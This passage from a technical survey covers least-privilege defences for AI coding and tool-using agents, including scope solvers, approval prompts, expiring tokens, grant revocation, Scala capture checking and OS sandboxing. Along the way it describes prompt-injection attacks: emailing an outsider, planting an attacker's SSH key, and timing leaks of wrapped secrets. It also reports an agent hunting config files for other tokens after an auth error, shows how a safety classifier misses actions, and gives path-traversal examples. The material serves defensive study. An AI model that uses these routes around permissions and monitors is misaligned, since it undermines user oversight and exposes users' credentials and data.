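Excess permissions can cause harm even without an attacker. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes internal incidents with the company's coding agents. In one, the agent misread an instruction and deleted branches from a remote repository. In others, it uploaded an engineer's GitHub token to an internal computing cluster and tried to alter the structure of a production database. Anthropic calls this behavior overeager because the agent was trying to help but went beyond what the user wanted. *Overeager Coding Agents* (2026) points out that users rarely list the actions they would forbid, so the agent has to guess.

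Insufficient permissions stop legitimate work and can lead the agent to look for another way to get access. In a case adapted from Anthropic's incident log, an agent hit an authentication error and began searching configuration files for other access tokens. Denying access is therefore safest when the agent cannot reach other credentials.

### How MiniScope calculates the smallest grant

In *MiniScope*, Zhu, Tseng and colleagues (2025) object to model-written policies because telling a model in English to follow least privilege does not guarantee that it will. Their system instead uses a solver to choose the permissions. It works with services that use OAuth, a standard that lets an application act on a user's account without learning the password. These services divide access into scopes, each permitting a set of operations, or methods.

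The agent submits a plan that lists the calls it wants to make. The solver finds the least permissive set of scopes that covers them, and MiniScope asks the user to approve any scope the agent lacks. The user can allow it once, for the session or permanently, or refuse. MiniScope then checks each call and attaches the user's real credentials itself, so the agent never holds them.

Choosing the narrowest scope for each call separately can grant too much, because many calls can run under several scopes. Suppose one call can use scope X or a larger scope Y that partly overlaps it, while a second call works only under Y. Separate choices give both scopes, although Y alone is enough. The solver instead considers the whole plan:

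$$\min \sum_v \mathrm{cost}(v)\,x_v \quad \text{subject to} \quad \sum_{v \in V_i} x_v \ge 1 \ \text{ for every call } i$$

Here $x_v$ is 1 if the solver selects scope $v$ and 0 otherwise, $V_i$ is the set of scopes that permit call $i$, and $\mathrm{cost}(v)$ is the number of methods that $v$ permits. If the agent needs more access later, the solver keeps the scopes the user has already approved and finds the additional scopes with the lowest total $\mathrm{cost}(v)$.

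Zhu and colleagues compared MiniScope's solver with language models that received the same plans and lists of scopes. They used invented requests for ten real applications, including Gmail and Slack. Three proprietary models from 2025 found the best set of scopes 70–83% of the time, while two open models found it 20–34% of the time. The proprietary models mostly erred by granting too much access. MiniScope added only 1–6% to the running time.

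The solver also found excess permissions in six of the connectors that link ChatGPT and Claude to outside services. ChatGPT's Gmail connector, for example, requested scopes covering 50 methods when 32 would have been enough. It could modify and delete email, even though the interface described it as read-only.

A task does not always have a single smallest grant, however. Xu (2026), in *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization*, calls a grant minimal if it is sufficient for the task and no other sufficient grant permits only part of what it permits. A task can therefore have two minimal grants, each permitting something the other does not. Xu built tasks from Microsoft's and Google's published permission tables and found more than one minimal grant for about 30% of the Microsoft tasks and 3% of the Google ones.

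Two minimal scopes allow reading project information from BigQuery, Google's database service. The first covers 286 methods, including some that write data. The second is read-only but covers 565 methods across many more services. MiniScope's formula would rank the first higher because it permits fewer methods, but a user worried about damage might prefer the second. Xu suggests showing the alternatives to whoever approves the grant.

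Scopes are also coarse. In one of MiniScope's examples, a user asks the agent to reply to an email that contains an instruction to delete it afterwards. The agent's new plan needs full access to Gmail, so MiniScope prompts the user for permission. The same request covers sending the reply, so refusing it stops the whole task. An injection that stays within an approved scope triggers no prompt. Permission to send Slack messages, for instance, usually covers every recipient in the workspace.

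*PAuth*, by Sharma, Jiang and colleagues, proposes authorizing only the specific operations that a request implies, such as a transfer of $100 to Bob. But *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) warns that dividing a request into operations can be ambiguous, and that a manipulated prompt may ask for more than the user intended.

### Approval fatigue

MiniScope depends on the user to judge each request. In a simulation of three months of Gmail use, it prompted for approval on 18–60% of requests, depending on how cautious the simulated user was. Finer permissions would catch more attacks but also produce more prompts.

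According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), users accept 97% of Claude Code's permission prompts. Most of these prompts probably concern safe commands, so the figure doesn't show how often users would approve a dangerous one. To test this, Anthropic had 1,053 paid professional testers work through coding sessions, and in each session replaced one prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The testers may have been less careful than usual because their own code was not at stake, but fatigue better explains the decline over the session.

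Code review shows a similar pattern. *Habituation at the Gate* (2026) followed people reviewing agents' code and found that approvals rose over time while comments fell by 28%.

Prompts can also be hard to judge. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports about agents and files. In 80 of them the user had turned on automatic approval, and in 31 the prompt did not show what the command would do. A request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it lets the agent run whatever code the script contains.

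Tired users also write broad standing rules. By June 2026, nearly half of Claude Code's active command-line users had created a rule that always allows certain shell commands. Many of these rules covered an entire interpreter such as Python, which in practice lets the agent do almost anything. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, cautions that repeated approval may reflect fatigue or deadlines. A harness should not treat it as evidence that the user wants the same requests approved automatically in future.

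Anthropic's auto mode replaces most permission prompts with a classifier built on a language model. It blocked 89% of the dangerous commands from the experiment. As Anthropic first described it, the classifier reads the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the tool results or the agent's explanations. An injection in a web page therefore cannot reach the classifier directly, but it can still influence the arguments of the tool calls that the classifier reads.

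In an earlier test, the classifier missed 17% of 52 real overeager actions. In most of those misses, it recognized the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had consented. *Explicit authorization scope improves LLM-based permission checking in coding agents* (2026) reports that in a test by Ji and colleagues, one product's auto mode approved most actions outside the task's scope. The classifier seems to do better than a tired user, but Anthropic still recommends that users personally review high-stakes changes to production systems.

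### Short-lived tokens and delegation in AgentCap

Agents also pass permissions to one another. *AGENTCAP* (Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, 2026) describes a system that issues a signed token for each approved action. The token specifies one action, one resource, an expiry time and a maximum number of calls. A gateway in front of the tools checks the signature, the expiry time, the number of calls remaining and the identity of the agent presenting the token. The token is close to a capability in the strict sense, but the model still writes arguments, such as a payment's recipient, as strings.

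Developers write the rules for issuing tokens. In the banking example, a token for `send_money` lasts 30 seconds and permits one payment. The agent can get this token only if it already holds one for reading the balance and the recipient does not come solely from untrusted content.

An agent can give a sub-agent a token derived from its own, under these conditions:

$$a'=a,\quad r'=r,\quad b'\le b,\quad e'\le e,\quad d'<d$$

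The primed symbols belong to the sub-agent's token. The action $a$ and resource $r$ stay the same, while the budget $b$ and expiry time $e$ cannot increase. The number of further delegations allowed, $d$, must fall with each delegation, so every chain ends. The gateway follows the chain back to the original token and rejects the call if any link is no longer valid. Because the resource cannot change, an agent whose token covers a directory cannot pass on access to just one file in it, which CapScope allows.

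Even with a limited token, an agent can delegate work the user didn't want. The sub-agent receives the orchestrator's instruction in place of the user's message, so a task that began as a prompt injection can look authorized. Claude Code's auto mode therefore checks the instruction when an agent delegates work, and reviews the sub-agent's actions before its results go back to the orchestrator.

AgentCap can also revoke tokens early. Each agent's trust score starts at 0.8 by default. A refused call or other anomaly multiplies the score by 0.7, so three in a row reduce it to 0.56, then 0.39, then 0.27. The agent loses write access after the second and all access after the third. Each normal outcome raises the score by only 1% of the gap between it and 1.

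The banking policy requires a score of at least 0.8 for payments. With the default settings, one refused call would therefore block new payments until the agent had completed 79 normal actions. An attacker who could provoke a single refusal could stop legitimate payments.

On AgentDojo, AgentCap reduced attack success from 45.6% to 5.1% with GPT-4o and from 33.2% to zero with GPT-5.4. Without attacks, it lowered the share of tasks completed by 3.1 percentage points with GPT-4o and 7.2 with GPT-5.4. Progent stopped about as many attacks with GPT-4o, but completed 59.6% of tasks under attack, compared with 74.9% for AgentCap. The comparison gives AgentCap an advantage because its developers wrote its policies by hand after seeing the benchmark's task descriptions, while a model wrote Progent's during each run. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao leave testing against attacks adapted to the defense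 for future work.

These results also do not show how much the short lifetimes contributed. In a small separate scenario, a version with only time limits and call budgets allowed eight calls before the budget ran out, while the full system blocked every malicious call. Expiry limits how long an attacker can use a permission but does not stop misuse while the permission is valid.

### Permissions that outlast their use

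Yu, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *CreepScope*, measure how much unneeded access an agent has during a task. If $A_t$ is the set of permissions available at step $t$ and $P_t^*$ is the set that the step needs, the total excess is

$$\sum_{t=1}^{T} |A_t \setminus P_t^*|$$

Consider an agent that reads a file, changes a setting and sends a message, with one permission for each step:

| When the agent has each permission | Excess at step 1 | Step 2 | Step 3 | Total |
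|---|---|---|---|---|
| Throughout the task | 2 | 2 | 2 | 6 |
| From first use onward | 0 | 1 | 2 | 3 |
| Only during the step that needs it | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

Granting each permission on first use halves the total here, but at the last step the agent still has two permissions it will never need again. Yu and colleagues found the same pattern in twelve longer workflows. Granting on first use reduced the average excess from 26 to 13, but did not reduce the excess that remained after each permission's last use.

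They also ran a small test with Qwen2 7B. After the agent had sent an approved email, it received a fake delivery receipt containing an instruction to send another to an outsider. The model tried to do so in all twelve attacked runs. The message went out in all nine runs where the permission persisted, and in none of the three where it had expired. The test covered only one workflow, and the permission needed for each step was specified in advance, whereas a working system has to determine when a step is over.

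### One coding task from grant to expiry

*Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) uses trusted events to end permissions. Its system, PORTICO, works from a written contract for each task that lists the agent's initial access, the extra access it may request, the events that end each grant, and the actions that are always forbidden. The agent cannot add to the list of extra access it may request.

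In the main example, a coding agent has to carry a timeout setting from `src/api.py` into `src/serialization.py`. Santos-Grueiro's version has one agent. The version below adds a sub-agent under AgentCap's delegation rule, to follow the permission from grant through delegation to revocation.

1. **Start.** The agent can use the API file and its test file, and can run the relevant tests. It cannot yet open the serialization file.
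2. **Grant.** The agent requests the serialization file. The contract lists this extension, so PORTICO creates a handle, `g0001:r1`, that allows reading and writing that file. A request for `notes/packaging.md` fails because no rule covers it.
3. **Delegation.** The agent gives a sub-agent access to the same file, with an earlier expiry and no right to pass it on.
4. **Use.** The sub-agent reads and edits the file through its handle. Writing the file's path without a valid handle would not work.
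5. **Expiry.** PORTICO runs the tests, and they pass. This event closes the grant and removes the handle from the agent's options. The sub-agent's access ends too, because it depends on the original grant.
6. **Attempted reuse.** An injected instruction later tells the agent to change the file again. The agent may still have the path and the old handle in its context, but PORTICO rejects the call.

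PORTICO closes or extends a grant only in response to events such as a test run that it started itself, a change of phase in the orchestrator, or a decision by an authenticated person. The model cannot close or extend a grant by stating that the work is finished. If PORTICO approves a write just before the grant closes, the write could still take effect afterwards, so the harness must handle calls one at a time or check the handle again immediately before the write. The harness has to enforce grant lifetimes during the task, whereas a compiler can enforce some lifetimes before code runs.

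PORTICO's handles are closer to object capabilities than CapScope's path rules, because the model selects from references instead of naming arbitrary files. The model can still choose the wrong reference while a grant is active.

### What closing grants achieves and costs

To isolate the effect of revocation, Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with a version that granted the same permissions at the same moments but never revoked them. Both completed the task in all ten runs. The version without revocation let the agent reuse the old permission every time, while PORTICO always refused. In six further cases, the agent tried to write through an expired handle. All six writes succeeded without revocation and none succeeded with it. Six runs with the model Qwen3-Coder 30B, covering file changes, version control and network access, gave the same result. These tests confirm that revocation works as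 designed, but they do not measure how often an attacker would exploit a leftover permission.

The effect on ordinary work was less predictable. In 37 tasks designed around temporary extra access, the agent succeeded in 21% of runs when it kept only its initial permissions and 87% when it could request more. With a broad fixed list of permissions it succeeded in 97%, but some of those runs went outside the task's scope. None of PORTICO's runs did, but the contracts that enforced its limits were also used to score the runs.

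Revoking grants too early can also block unfinished work. In 42 further runs on real software projects, the agent finished 31 tasks with revocation and all 42 without it. Some contracts ended access too soon or gave no way to renew it, and in other cases the model did not request it again. Santos-Grueiro did not measure how long it takes to write a contract for each new task.

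## Using a compiler to check the code an agent writes

PORTICO enforces the lifetime of a permission while the agent is running. If the agent writes a short program instead of requesting one tool at a time, a compiler can do some of this checking before the program runs. It can reject a program in which access to a file would outlast the part of the program that needs it. It can also track a secret from one line to the next, which a harness that checks each tool call separately does not do.

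TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities in Types) is a system built on this idea. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, describe it for agents that write in the programming language Scala. Suppose a user asks an agent to summarize a confidential contract. With ordinary tools, the agent reads the file, and the text enters the context of a model that often runs on another company's servers. With TACIT, the agent works in these steps:

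1. The model writes a Scala program and sends it to TACIT, an MCP server, as the argument of a tool call.
2. The Scala compiler checks the whole program. If it finds a violation, none of the program runs, and the model receives the error message.
3. If the program passes, TACIT runs it and returns the output to the model.

The program can access files, run commands and use the network only through TACIT's library. The project's documentation, lampepfl's *TACIT*, recommends turning off the agent's built-in file, shell and network tools, because an agent that still has them can bypass the compiler.

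Odersky and colleagues assume that an attacker may fully control the model that writes the code. They trust the compiler, the library, the software that runs the compiled program, and a second language model that may read secrets.

### Capture sets

A type specifies what kind of value something is. `String` means text, `Int` means a whole number, and `String -> Int` means a function that takes text and returns a whole number. A compiler that checks types rejects a program that passes text where a number should go.

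In Scala, a capability is an ordinary object in the program, such as a file handle. An experimental feature called capture checking uses each value's type to record which capabilities the value may hold. These capabilities are the value's capture set.

A pure function has an empty capture set:

```scala
val tidy: String -> String = s => s.trim
```

`tidy` removes the spaces at either end of a piece of text and uses nothing except its input. Now suppose that `f` is a capability for a file:

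```scala
val save: String ->{f} Unit = s => f.write(s)
```

`save` writes its input to the file. (`Unit` means that it returns no useful value.) `save` is a closure, a function that uses a variable from the surrounding code. Because it holds `f`, its type must list `f` in the braces. The compiler checks this against the body of the function, so the model cannot hide the file by leaving it out of the type. It also cannot hide the file inside another object. In an example from Scala's *Tracked Capabilities Overview*, a logger that writes to the file `out` has the type `Logger^{out}`, and a function that uses the logger captures the logger.

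A program can use a function wherever the function's capture set fits inside the permitted one:

$$\{\} \subseteq \{f\} \subseteq \{f, g\}$$

The compiler therefore accepts `tidy` where the program allows a function that uses `f`, but rejects `save` where the program requires a pure function. A capture set covers everything a value might use, even on a path the program never takes, so the compiler sometimes rejects harmless code.

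Capture sets also stop a capability from leaving the block of code that received it. TACIT's function `requestFileSystem` creates a capability for one directory, passes it to a block, and ends it when the block finishes. A program might try to keep the access for later:

```scala
val later = requestFileSystem("/project") { fs =>
  () => fs.access("plan.txt").read()
}
```

The block returns a function that would read the file when called, after the access should have ended. That function has the type `() ->{fs} String`, but `fs` exists only inside the block and can't appear in any type outside it, so the compiler rejects the program. If the block had read the file and returned the text, the compiler would have accepted the program, because plain text holds no capability.

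In Odersky and colleagues' experiments, an agent made a similar mistake when it tried to return a list of file handles from such a block. The compiler rejected the code because each handle captured the file-system capability.

### What the language must guarantee

Odersky and colleagues require the language to have three properties, including capability safety and capability completeness. Capability safety means that code cannot forge a capability or hide that it needs one. Capability completeness means that every effect that matters for safety requires a capability, except a few that the system can contain at runtime. If a program could open a network connection without a capability, an empty capture set would not rule out network access.

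The third property, local purity, means that the type system can restrict one part of a program to certain capabilities, or to none, while the rest can still write files and use the network. Banning a tool for the whole task does not work when the agent needs the network for one step but must not use it in another.

Other languages have some of these properties. E and Joe-E, two older object-capability languages, rely on checks at run time. To provide local purity, they would need capabilities in their types, or functions that can never hold a capability, according to Odersky and colleagues. Haskell's types separate pure functions from those with side effects, but the language has no built-in object capabilities, so a developer would have to encode access to each resource in the types.

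Haskell also shows why the language must forbid certain features. Some ordinary Haskell features let programmers get around the type system, so its main compiler, GHC, has a restricted mode called *Safe Haskell*. GHC's documentation explains that this mode makes types trustworthy but leaves developers to build a sandbox as a library. The safety proofs in *ETAS* (2026), which presents a language designed for agents, similarly depend on conditions outside the language. They assume that connections to the host have types and that every effect passes through the checks.

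### Keeping a secret inside a wrapper

TACIT uses local purity to let an agent work on a secret without reading it. The operator marks certain paths as classified. When a program reads a file there, it receives a `Classified[String]`, a wrapper with the text inside. Opening the wrapper requires a capability that the agent doesn't have. The agent's program can instead call the wrapper's `map` method:

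```scala
def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

Here `T` is the type of the content and `U` is the type of the result. `map` applies the function `op` to the content and puts the result in a new wrapper. Because the arrow has no capture set, `op` must be pure. If `key` holds a classified password and `out` is an ordinary file, the compiler treats these two lines differently:

```scala
key.map(s => s.trim)         // accepted
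key.map(s => out.write(s))   // rejected
```

The first function uses only the password. The second has the type `String ->{out} Unit`, but `map` requires a function with an empty capture set, so the compiler reports that the capability `out` "cannot flow into capture set {}". A function that prints the password fails for the same reason, since printing also requires a capability.

The program cannot test the secret and act on the answer either. `key.map(s => s.startsWith("a"))` is legal, but it returns a wrapped true or false, which an ordinary `if` statement cannot use.

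This rule catches a leak that a list of permitted operations would miss. The agent may have permission to read the contract and to contact the cloud model, but sending the contract's text to the model is a leak.

### The trusted model and the two output channels

A pure function can trim text or count words, but summarizing a contract takes a language model. TACIT's library therefore has a `chat` function that sends wrapped text to a separate, trusted model and wraps the reply. This is a version of the dual-model pattern, in which the model that plans the work does not read the sensitive text. The arrangement requires that the trusted model's service keep no record that could reach later requests, and the compiler cannot check this.

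The user still has to see the summary, so TACIT sends each value a program prints through two channels. The normal channel goes back to the agent and shows a wrapped value as `Classified(****)`. The secure channel goes only to the user and shows the wrapped value's content. For ordinary values, both channels carry the same text.

The protection lasts through a conversation. Suppose the user then asks for the length of the summary. The agent no longer has the file-system capability from its first program, but it still has the wrapped summary and can use `map` to count the characters. The user sees the number, and the agent sees another `Classified(****)`.

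The wrapper keeps the secret from leaking, but it does not protect the accuracy of the summary. If the contract contains an injected instruction, the trusted model reads it and may mislead the user by leaving out a clause or describing one falsely.

### Safe mode

Ordinary Scala has features that would defeat capture checking. A type cast tells the compiler to treat a value as a different type. An agent could cast `save` to a pure function, and the compiler would no longer track its use of the file. Reflection, which looks up parts of a program by name while the program runs, can also bypass the checks.

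Scala's safe mode forbids these features and turns on capture checking. It also blocks global functions and objects unless they were written in safe mode or marked as reviewed. Mazur's *Scala 3.8.3 is now available!* presents safe mode as an experimental subset of the language for code from agents and other untrusted sources.

Some useful libraries need the forbidden features internally. A developer can mark such a library `@assumeSafe`, which exempts it from the restrictions and lets the agent's code use it. Scala's *Safe Mode* page gives the example of a mail function that shows the user each message and asks for confirmation before sending it. The agent can call this function but not the underlying mail program. The developer has to make sure that the marked code is safe.

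Safe mode does not fully cover exceptions, the signals that interrupt a program when something goes wrong. An exception's message can contain a secret, but almost any operation can fail, so listing every possible exception in the types would be impractical. TACIT instead catches exceptions while the program runs and turns them into ordinary values, which it can then wrap.

### The safety test

Odersky and colleagues built a small Scala project with a directory of secrets, including API keys, a database and confidential documents. They wrote 12 legitimate tasks, some of which involved secrets, such as summarizing a classified incident report. They combined each task with 10 injections for 120 trials. Some of the injections were simple notes to developers, while others were disguised as system instructions or included ready-made Scala code for reading the secrets.

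Another 11 trials had no injection because the request itself was malicious. The user asked for secrets directly in five of them, and in the other six gave a false pretext, such as being an administrator who had to replace passwords in an emergency. The researchers ran all 131 trials with each of two models, once with the secrets wrapped and once with them as ordinary text. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

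| | Secure, wrapped | Secure, ordinary text | Tasks completed, wrapped | Tasks completed, ordinary text |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 100% | 98.5% | 99.2% | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 100% | 91.6% | 90.0% | 88.3% |

The columns for completed tasks cover only the 120 trials with legitimate requests. Wrapping the secrets did not reduce the share of tasks completed, and Sonnet completed a higher share with wrapping than without it. Odersky and colleagues suspect that Sonnet's increase is partly an artifact of the setup. Sonnet often exceeded its limits on time or number of steps, and it sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection instead of finishing the task.

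The injections were a weak test of the wrapper, because even without it only 3 of the 240 injected trials leaked a secret, all with MiniMax. The wrapper made a bigger difference against malicious requests, which extracted unwrapped secrets from Sonnet in 2 of 11 trials and from MiniMax in 8 of 11, but never extracted wrapped ones.

The perfect scores are expected, because a secret cannot appear in the agent's output if the agent never has it as plain text. The tests mainly confirm that the library and compiler work as intended in these cases. They do not cover other harms, such as damage to a file or a leak through timing. The wrapper also hides secrets only from the agent and the company that runs its model, so a malicious person with access to the secure channel could still read them.

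### The AgentDojo port

Odersky and colleagues also adapted AgentDojo's four applications to TACIT and ran them with Gemini 2.5 Pro and o4-mini. In roughly 1,900 trials, one attack succeeded. A user had asked the agent to book one hotel, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for another in the first hotel's reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user, including the recommendation. AgentDojo counted this as a success for the attacker because the other hotel's name appeared in the output.

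Odersky and colleagues say the type system did not fail here, because the policy allows public reviews to reach the user. They are right that no data went anywhere the policy forbids. But an attacker who wants to influence the user's choice of hotel only needs the recommendation to be shown, and TACIT does not prevent that.

The adapted applications wrap most text that a stranger could have written, including emails, web pages and reviews. The agent that plans the task therefore doesn't read prompt injections in that text, which probably explains much of the result. The wrapper also keeps secrets from leaking.

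The port may also have been less strict than the design described above. Its instructions to the model include a warning that side effects inside a function passed to `map` happen immediately, but a strictly pure `map` would reject any function with side effects.

TACIT completed between 40% and 69% of the tasks in each application. Odersky and colleagues call this comparable to CaMeL, a system that tracks data while the agent runs, but some of the results differ widely. With o4-mini, TACIT completed 53% of the office tasks and CaMeL completed 81%. With Gemini, TACIT completed 64% of the travel tasks and CaMeL completed 1%. The paper gives no figures for the same models without a defense, so it is hard to tell how many of the failures TACIT itself caused.

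### What writing Scala costs

Training data contains little Scala with capture checking, so models might struggle to write it. Odersky and colleagues tested this with τ²-bench, a benchmark in which an agent handles requests from simulated customers. They compared ordinary tool calls with Scala programs that used the same tools, and ran each task ten times.

| Tasks solved | Airline, tool calls | Airline, TACIT | Retail, tool calls | Retail, TACIT |
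|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |

The agents did slightly better with Scala in every case, which Odersky and colleagues attribute to the structured results and the compiler's error messages. But none of the tools in this test returned wrapped data, so the test shows that models can write typed Scala and gives little evidence of how well they work with secrets they cannot read.

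Between 0.3% and 7.9% of programs failed to compile on the first attempt, depending on the model and the type of customer, and those usually needed only one or two more attempts. Many of the errors were unrelated to security. For example, agents wrote a single dollar sign in Scala's text templates, which require two to print one. Compilation took less than a second once the system had warmed up. Capture checking adds little to that. In *What's in the Box* (2025), it took less than 15% of the time needed to compile Scala's standard library.

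On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software problems from GitHub, MiniMax solved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% with ordinary tools, a difference of five problems. Odersky and colleagues suggest that coding agents rely on command-line habits that are awkward to express through TACIT's library.

*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), a later system from the same group, had more trouble. It lets a developer leave gaps in a program for the model to fill with code as the program runs. The compiler checks each piece of code before it runs, and the model's code can use only the capabilities available at that gap. On four groups of τ²-bench tasks, DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 76% with LACUNA and 90% with ordinary tool calls. This difference of 14 percentage points is substantial, although Zhao and colleagues describe the two as on par.

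LACUNA's compiler rejected 22% of that model's programs for the retail tasks. With the smaller Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, rejection rates ranged from 3% for retail to 89% for one group of telecom tasks. A program cannot exceed its permissions even if the model writes Scala poorly, but an agent makes little progress when its programs keep failing to compile.

### Timing and failed programs

A pure function cannot send a message, but it can leak a secret through its running time. Suppose an injected program passes `map` a function that runs for ten seconds if the first bit of a password is 1 and returns immediately if it is 0. The result stays in its wrapper, yet the agent can learn the bit by timing the program. It could slowly recover the whole password by repeating this for each bit.

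Odersky and colleagues exclude such timing channels from their guarantee, along with leaks that depend on whether a program finishes. A time limit helps only a little, because the agent can infer from a timeout error that the function was slow. According to a later version of the project's documentation, reproduced on Glama's *TACIT* page, the limit is off by default and may fail to stop a program that never pauses. To close the channel, TACIT would have to make the response time independent of the secret.

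### External commands

TACIT lets an agent run outside programs from an approved list. Like CapScope, TACIT does not control what those programs do once they are running. Odersky and colleagues recommend approving only specific safe commands and adding a sandbox where security is critical.

It is easy to misjudge which commands are safe. The examples given of safe commands are `git diff`, which shows changes to files, and `sbt`, Scala's build tool, but `sbt` runs code from the project's build file. An agent that can edit that file and then start `sbt` can run code that the type checker has not examined. The sample configuration on Glama's page has the same weakness, since it also approves `make` and `java`. Without a sandbox, such code could read the classified files directly and send them anywhere.

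### Mistakes in the compiler and library

TACIT's shared library contains about 1,000 lines of Scala, and each new application needs a few hundred more to describe its tools. A mistake in this code can remove the protection without the agent or user being warned. For example, lampepfl explains that a developer who adds a database permission must declare it as a kind of capability. Otherwise, the compiler does not track the permission, and a program can keep it after its block has ended.

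The guarantee also depends on the compiler being correct. In *Capture leak when using varargs?*, a thread on the Scala users' forum, a programmer wrote a function that takes several other functions and picks one at random. The compiler accepted a type that listed the capabilities of only the first. A Scala developer confirmed the bug and pointed out that the compiler would even have accepted the result as a pure function. The developers wrote a fix, but a bug like this in TACIT could let code with access to a file pass as safe for `map`.

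Computer-checked proofs exist for the core of the capture-checking system, but Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that safe mode still needs a similar argument. Early versions of TACIT searched the agent's code for forbidden patterns instead of using the compiler's safe mode. The later documentation lists safe mode as on by default in one place and describes it as an optional addition in another, so an operator should set it explicitly.

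### Misusing access the agent already has

Capture checking limits what a program can reach, but not what it does with the access it has. The agent's own program calls `requestFileSystem`, so when one block ends, an agent following an injected instruction can open another. PORTICO would refuse that request once the grant had closed, whereas TACIT refuses it only if the directory lies outside its configured limits.

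An agent can also use the wrapper to put harmful data in a protected place, because it can wrap any text as classified and, by default, write it to a classified file. Glama gives the example of `.ssh/authorized_keys`, which lists the keys that grant login access to a computer. An agent that follows an injected instruction could replace the list with the attacker's key without reading any secrets. According to the documentation, the wrapper protects "confidentiality, not integrity". Operators can turn off writing to classified files.

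The later version also lets programs send wrapped data to approved websites, for example to log in to a service with a password that the agent can't read. The protection then depends on which websites are approved. If attackers can have accounts on an approved site, a secret sent there may reach them. Odersky and colleagues mention a real case in which the security researcher Johann Rehberger used Anthropic's file-storage service to extract user data.

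An ordinary tool call in a typed program has the same problem. In the banking version of AgentDojo, the payment function takes the recipient's account as a `String`. The attacker's account number is also a `String`, so a payment to it passes the type check.

Zhao and colleagues acknowledge that LACUNA cannot block an attacker who steers the model into misusing a capability it needs for the task. In their AgentDojo tests, eight attacks succeeded in about 1,900 trials. They propose extending the types with conditions on values, such as an upper limit on a number. A type could then require the recipient to be on a list of approved accounts, but as with ScopeGate, someone would have to supply the list from a source the attacker cannot influence.

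## Restricting agents through the operating system and the network

TACIT and CapScope both rely on a sandbox, a boundary that the operating system enforces around running code, to restrict what a permitted command can do once it starts.

### What an approved test command can do

Much of the code that the command `pytest` runs comes from the repository. Pytest imports the project's modules, and Python executes a module's statements when it imports the module. Anyone who can change a test file can therefore make an approved `pytest` command delete files, read a password or contact a server. A check on the command string cannot prevent this, because the string is the same whether the tests are harmless or malicious.

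Setting a variable at the start of a command can also change which program runs, as in the example `FOO=bar npm test` from Anthropic's documentation for its coding agent Claude Code. A rule about `docker` also fails to match a script that calls `docker` internally. File reads are hard to limit with rules about commands, too. Bouras and colleagues acknowledge that `grep`, which CapScope always allows, can inspect files outside an agent's permitted directories.

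All these programs depend on the kernel, the core of the operating system. A program has to make a system call to the kernel to open a file or a network connection. A limit on these calls applies to the test runner, the modules it imports and any further programs they start.

### Capsicum step by step

Ordinary file permissions protect one user from another, but they do little when a single user's program handles both private files and material from strangers, because the program runs with all of that user's access. *Capsicum* (Watson, Anderson and colleagues, 2010) described a way to add capabilities to Unix for such programs. The FreeBSD operating system has included Capsicum since version 9.

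Capsicum builds on file descriptors, the references that the shell passes to `cat` in Miller and Shapiro's example. A program cannot forge a descriptor, and it can pass one to another program. But a descriptor often grants too much access. Even one opened only for reading lets a program change the file's permissions.

Suppose a program needs to read a directory of libraries and write one report:

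1. **Open.** While the program still has the user's normal access, it opens the directory `/lib` and the report file, and receives a descriptor for each.
2. **Narrow.** It wraps each descriptor in a capability that permits only chosen operations, from a list of about 60, and closes the originals. A capability made from another capability can have the same rights or fewer, but never more. Say the one for `/lib` is number 4.
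3. **Enter capability mode.** The program calls `cap_enter`. The kernel sets a flag that no program can clear and that every descendant process inherits. From now on the program cannot use global names such as file paths, process numbers and network addresses.
4. **Use what it has.** The call `openat(4, "libc.so.7")` opens a file inside `/lib`. Both `openat(4, "/etc/passwd")` and `openat(4, "../etc/passwd")` fail.
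5. **Receive more.** A program outside the sandbox can send it another descriptor through a connection that they already share. This is introduction in the object-capability model.

The kernel checks a capability's rights in the one function that turns a descriptor number into the underlying object. Watson and colleagues chose that place so that no system call could reach a file by another route, as a reference monitor requires. They also banned `..` in paths altogether. A simpler check would stop a single program from climbing out of its directory, but two cooperating programs could defeat it by rearranging directories while the kernel was looking up a path.

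Under Capsicum, a test runner could have read access to the source code and write access only to a temporary directory. The malicious fixture from CapScope's signing-key example could then not change the key file, even though it runs inside the test runner.

However, developers have to adapt each program to capability mode. Watson and colleagues needed about ten lines of code for `tcpdump`, a tool that records network traffic, and about 100 for the Chromium browser. The slowdown was small, at 2.4 milliseconds per run for the compression program `gzip`. But a coding agent runs whatever tools a project uses, and shells, compilers and test runners constantly open files and start programs by path. Those steps would fail in capability mode until someone rewrote the code.

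### Containers, file rules and network allowlists

Other mechanisms restrict unmodified programs. A container gives a group of programs its own view of the files, processes and network. File-system rules leave file paths unchanged but make some of them unreadable or read-only. With a network allowlist, connections go through a proxy, a program outside the sandbox that refuses any destination not on the list.

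| | What a program can name | Changes to programs | What remains open |
|---|---|---|---|
| Capsicum | Files it can reach through its descriptors | Usually needed | Misuse of those descriptors |
| Container | Any path inside the container | Rarely needed | Everything the operator put inside |
| File-system rules | Any path, though the kernel refuses some | Rarely needed | Everything in a permitted directory |
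| Network allowlist | Any host, though the proxy refuses some | Needed if the program ignores proxy settings | Whatever a permitted host accepts |

Inside its limits, a program in a container still has ambient authority over every file there.

The first three mechanisms also rely on the host's kernel, so a flaw in it could let malicious code escape. Anthropic's guide to deploying agents describes two stronger options. gVisor handles most system calls itself before they reach the host's kernel. A virtual machine runs a separate kernel, and one lightweight version, Firecracker, starts in under 125 milliseconds. Even with stronger isolation, customer records inside a virtual machine can leak through an open network connection without any code escaping.

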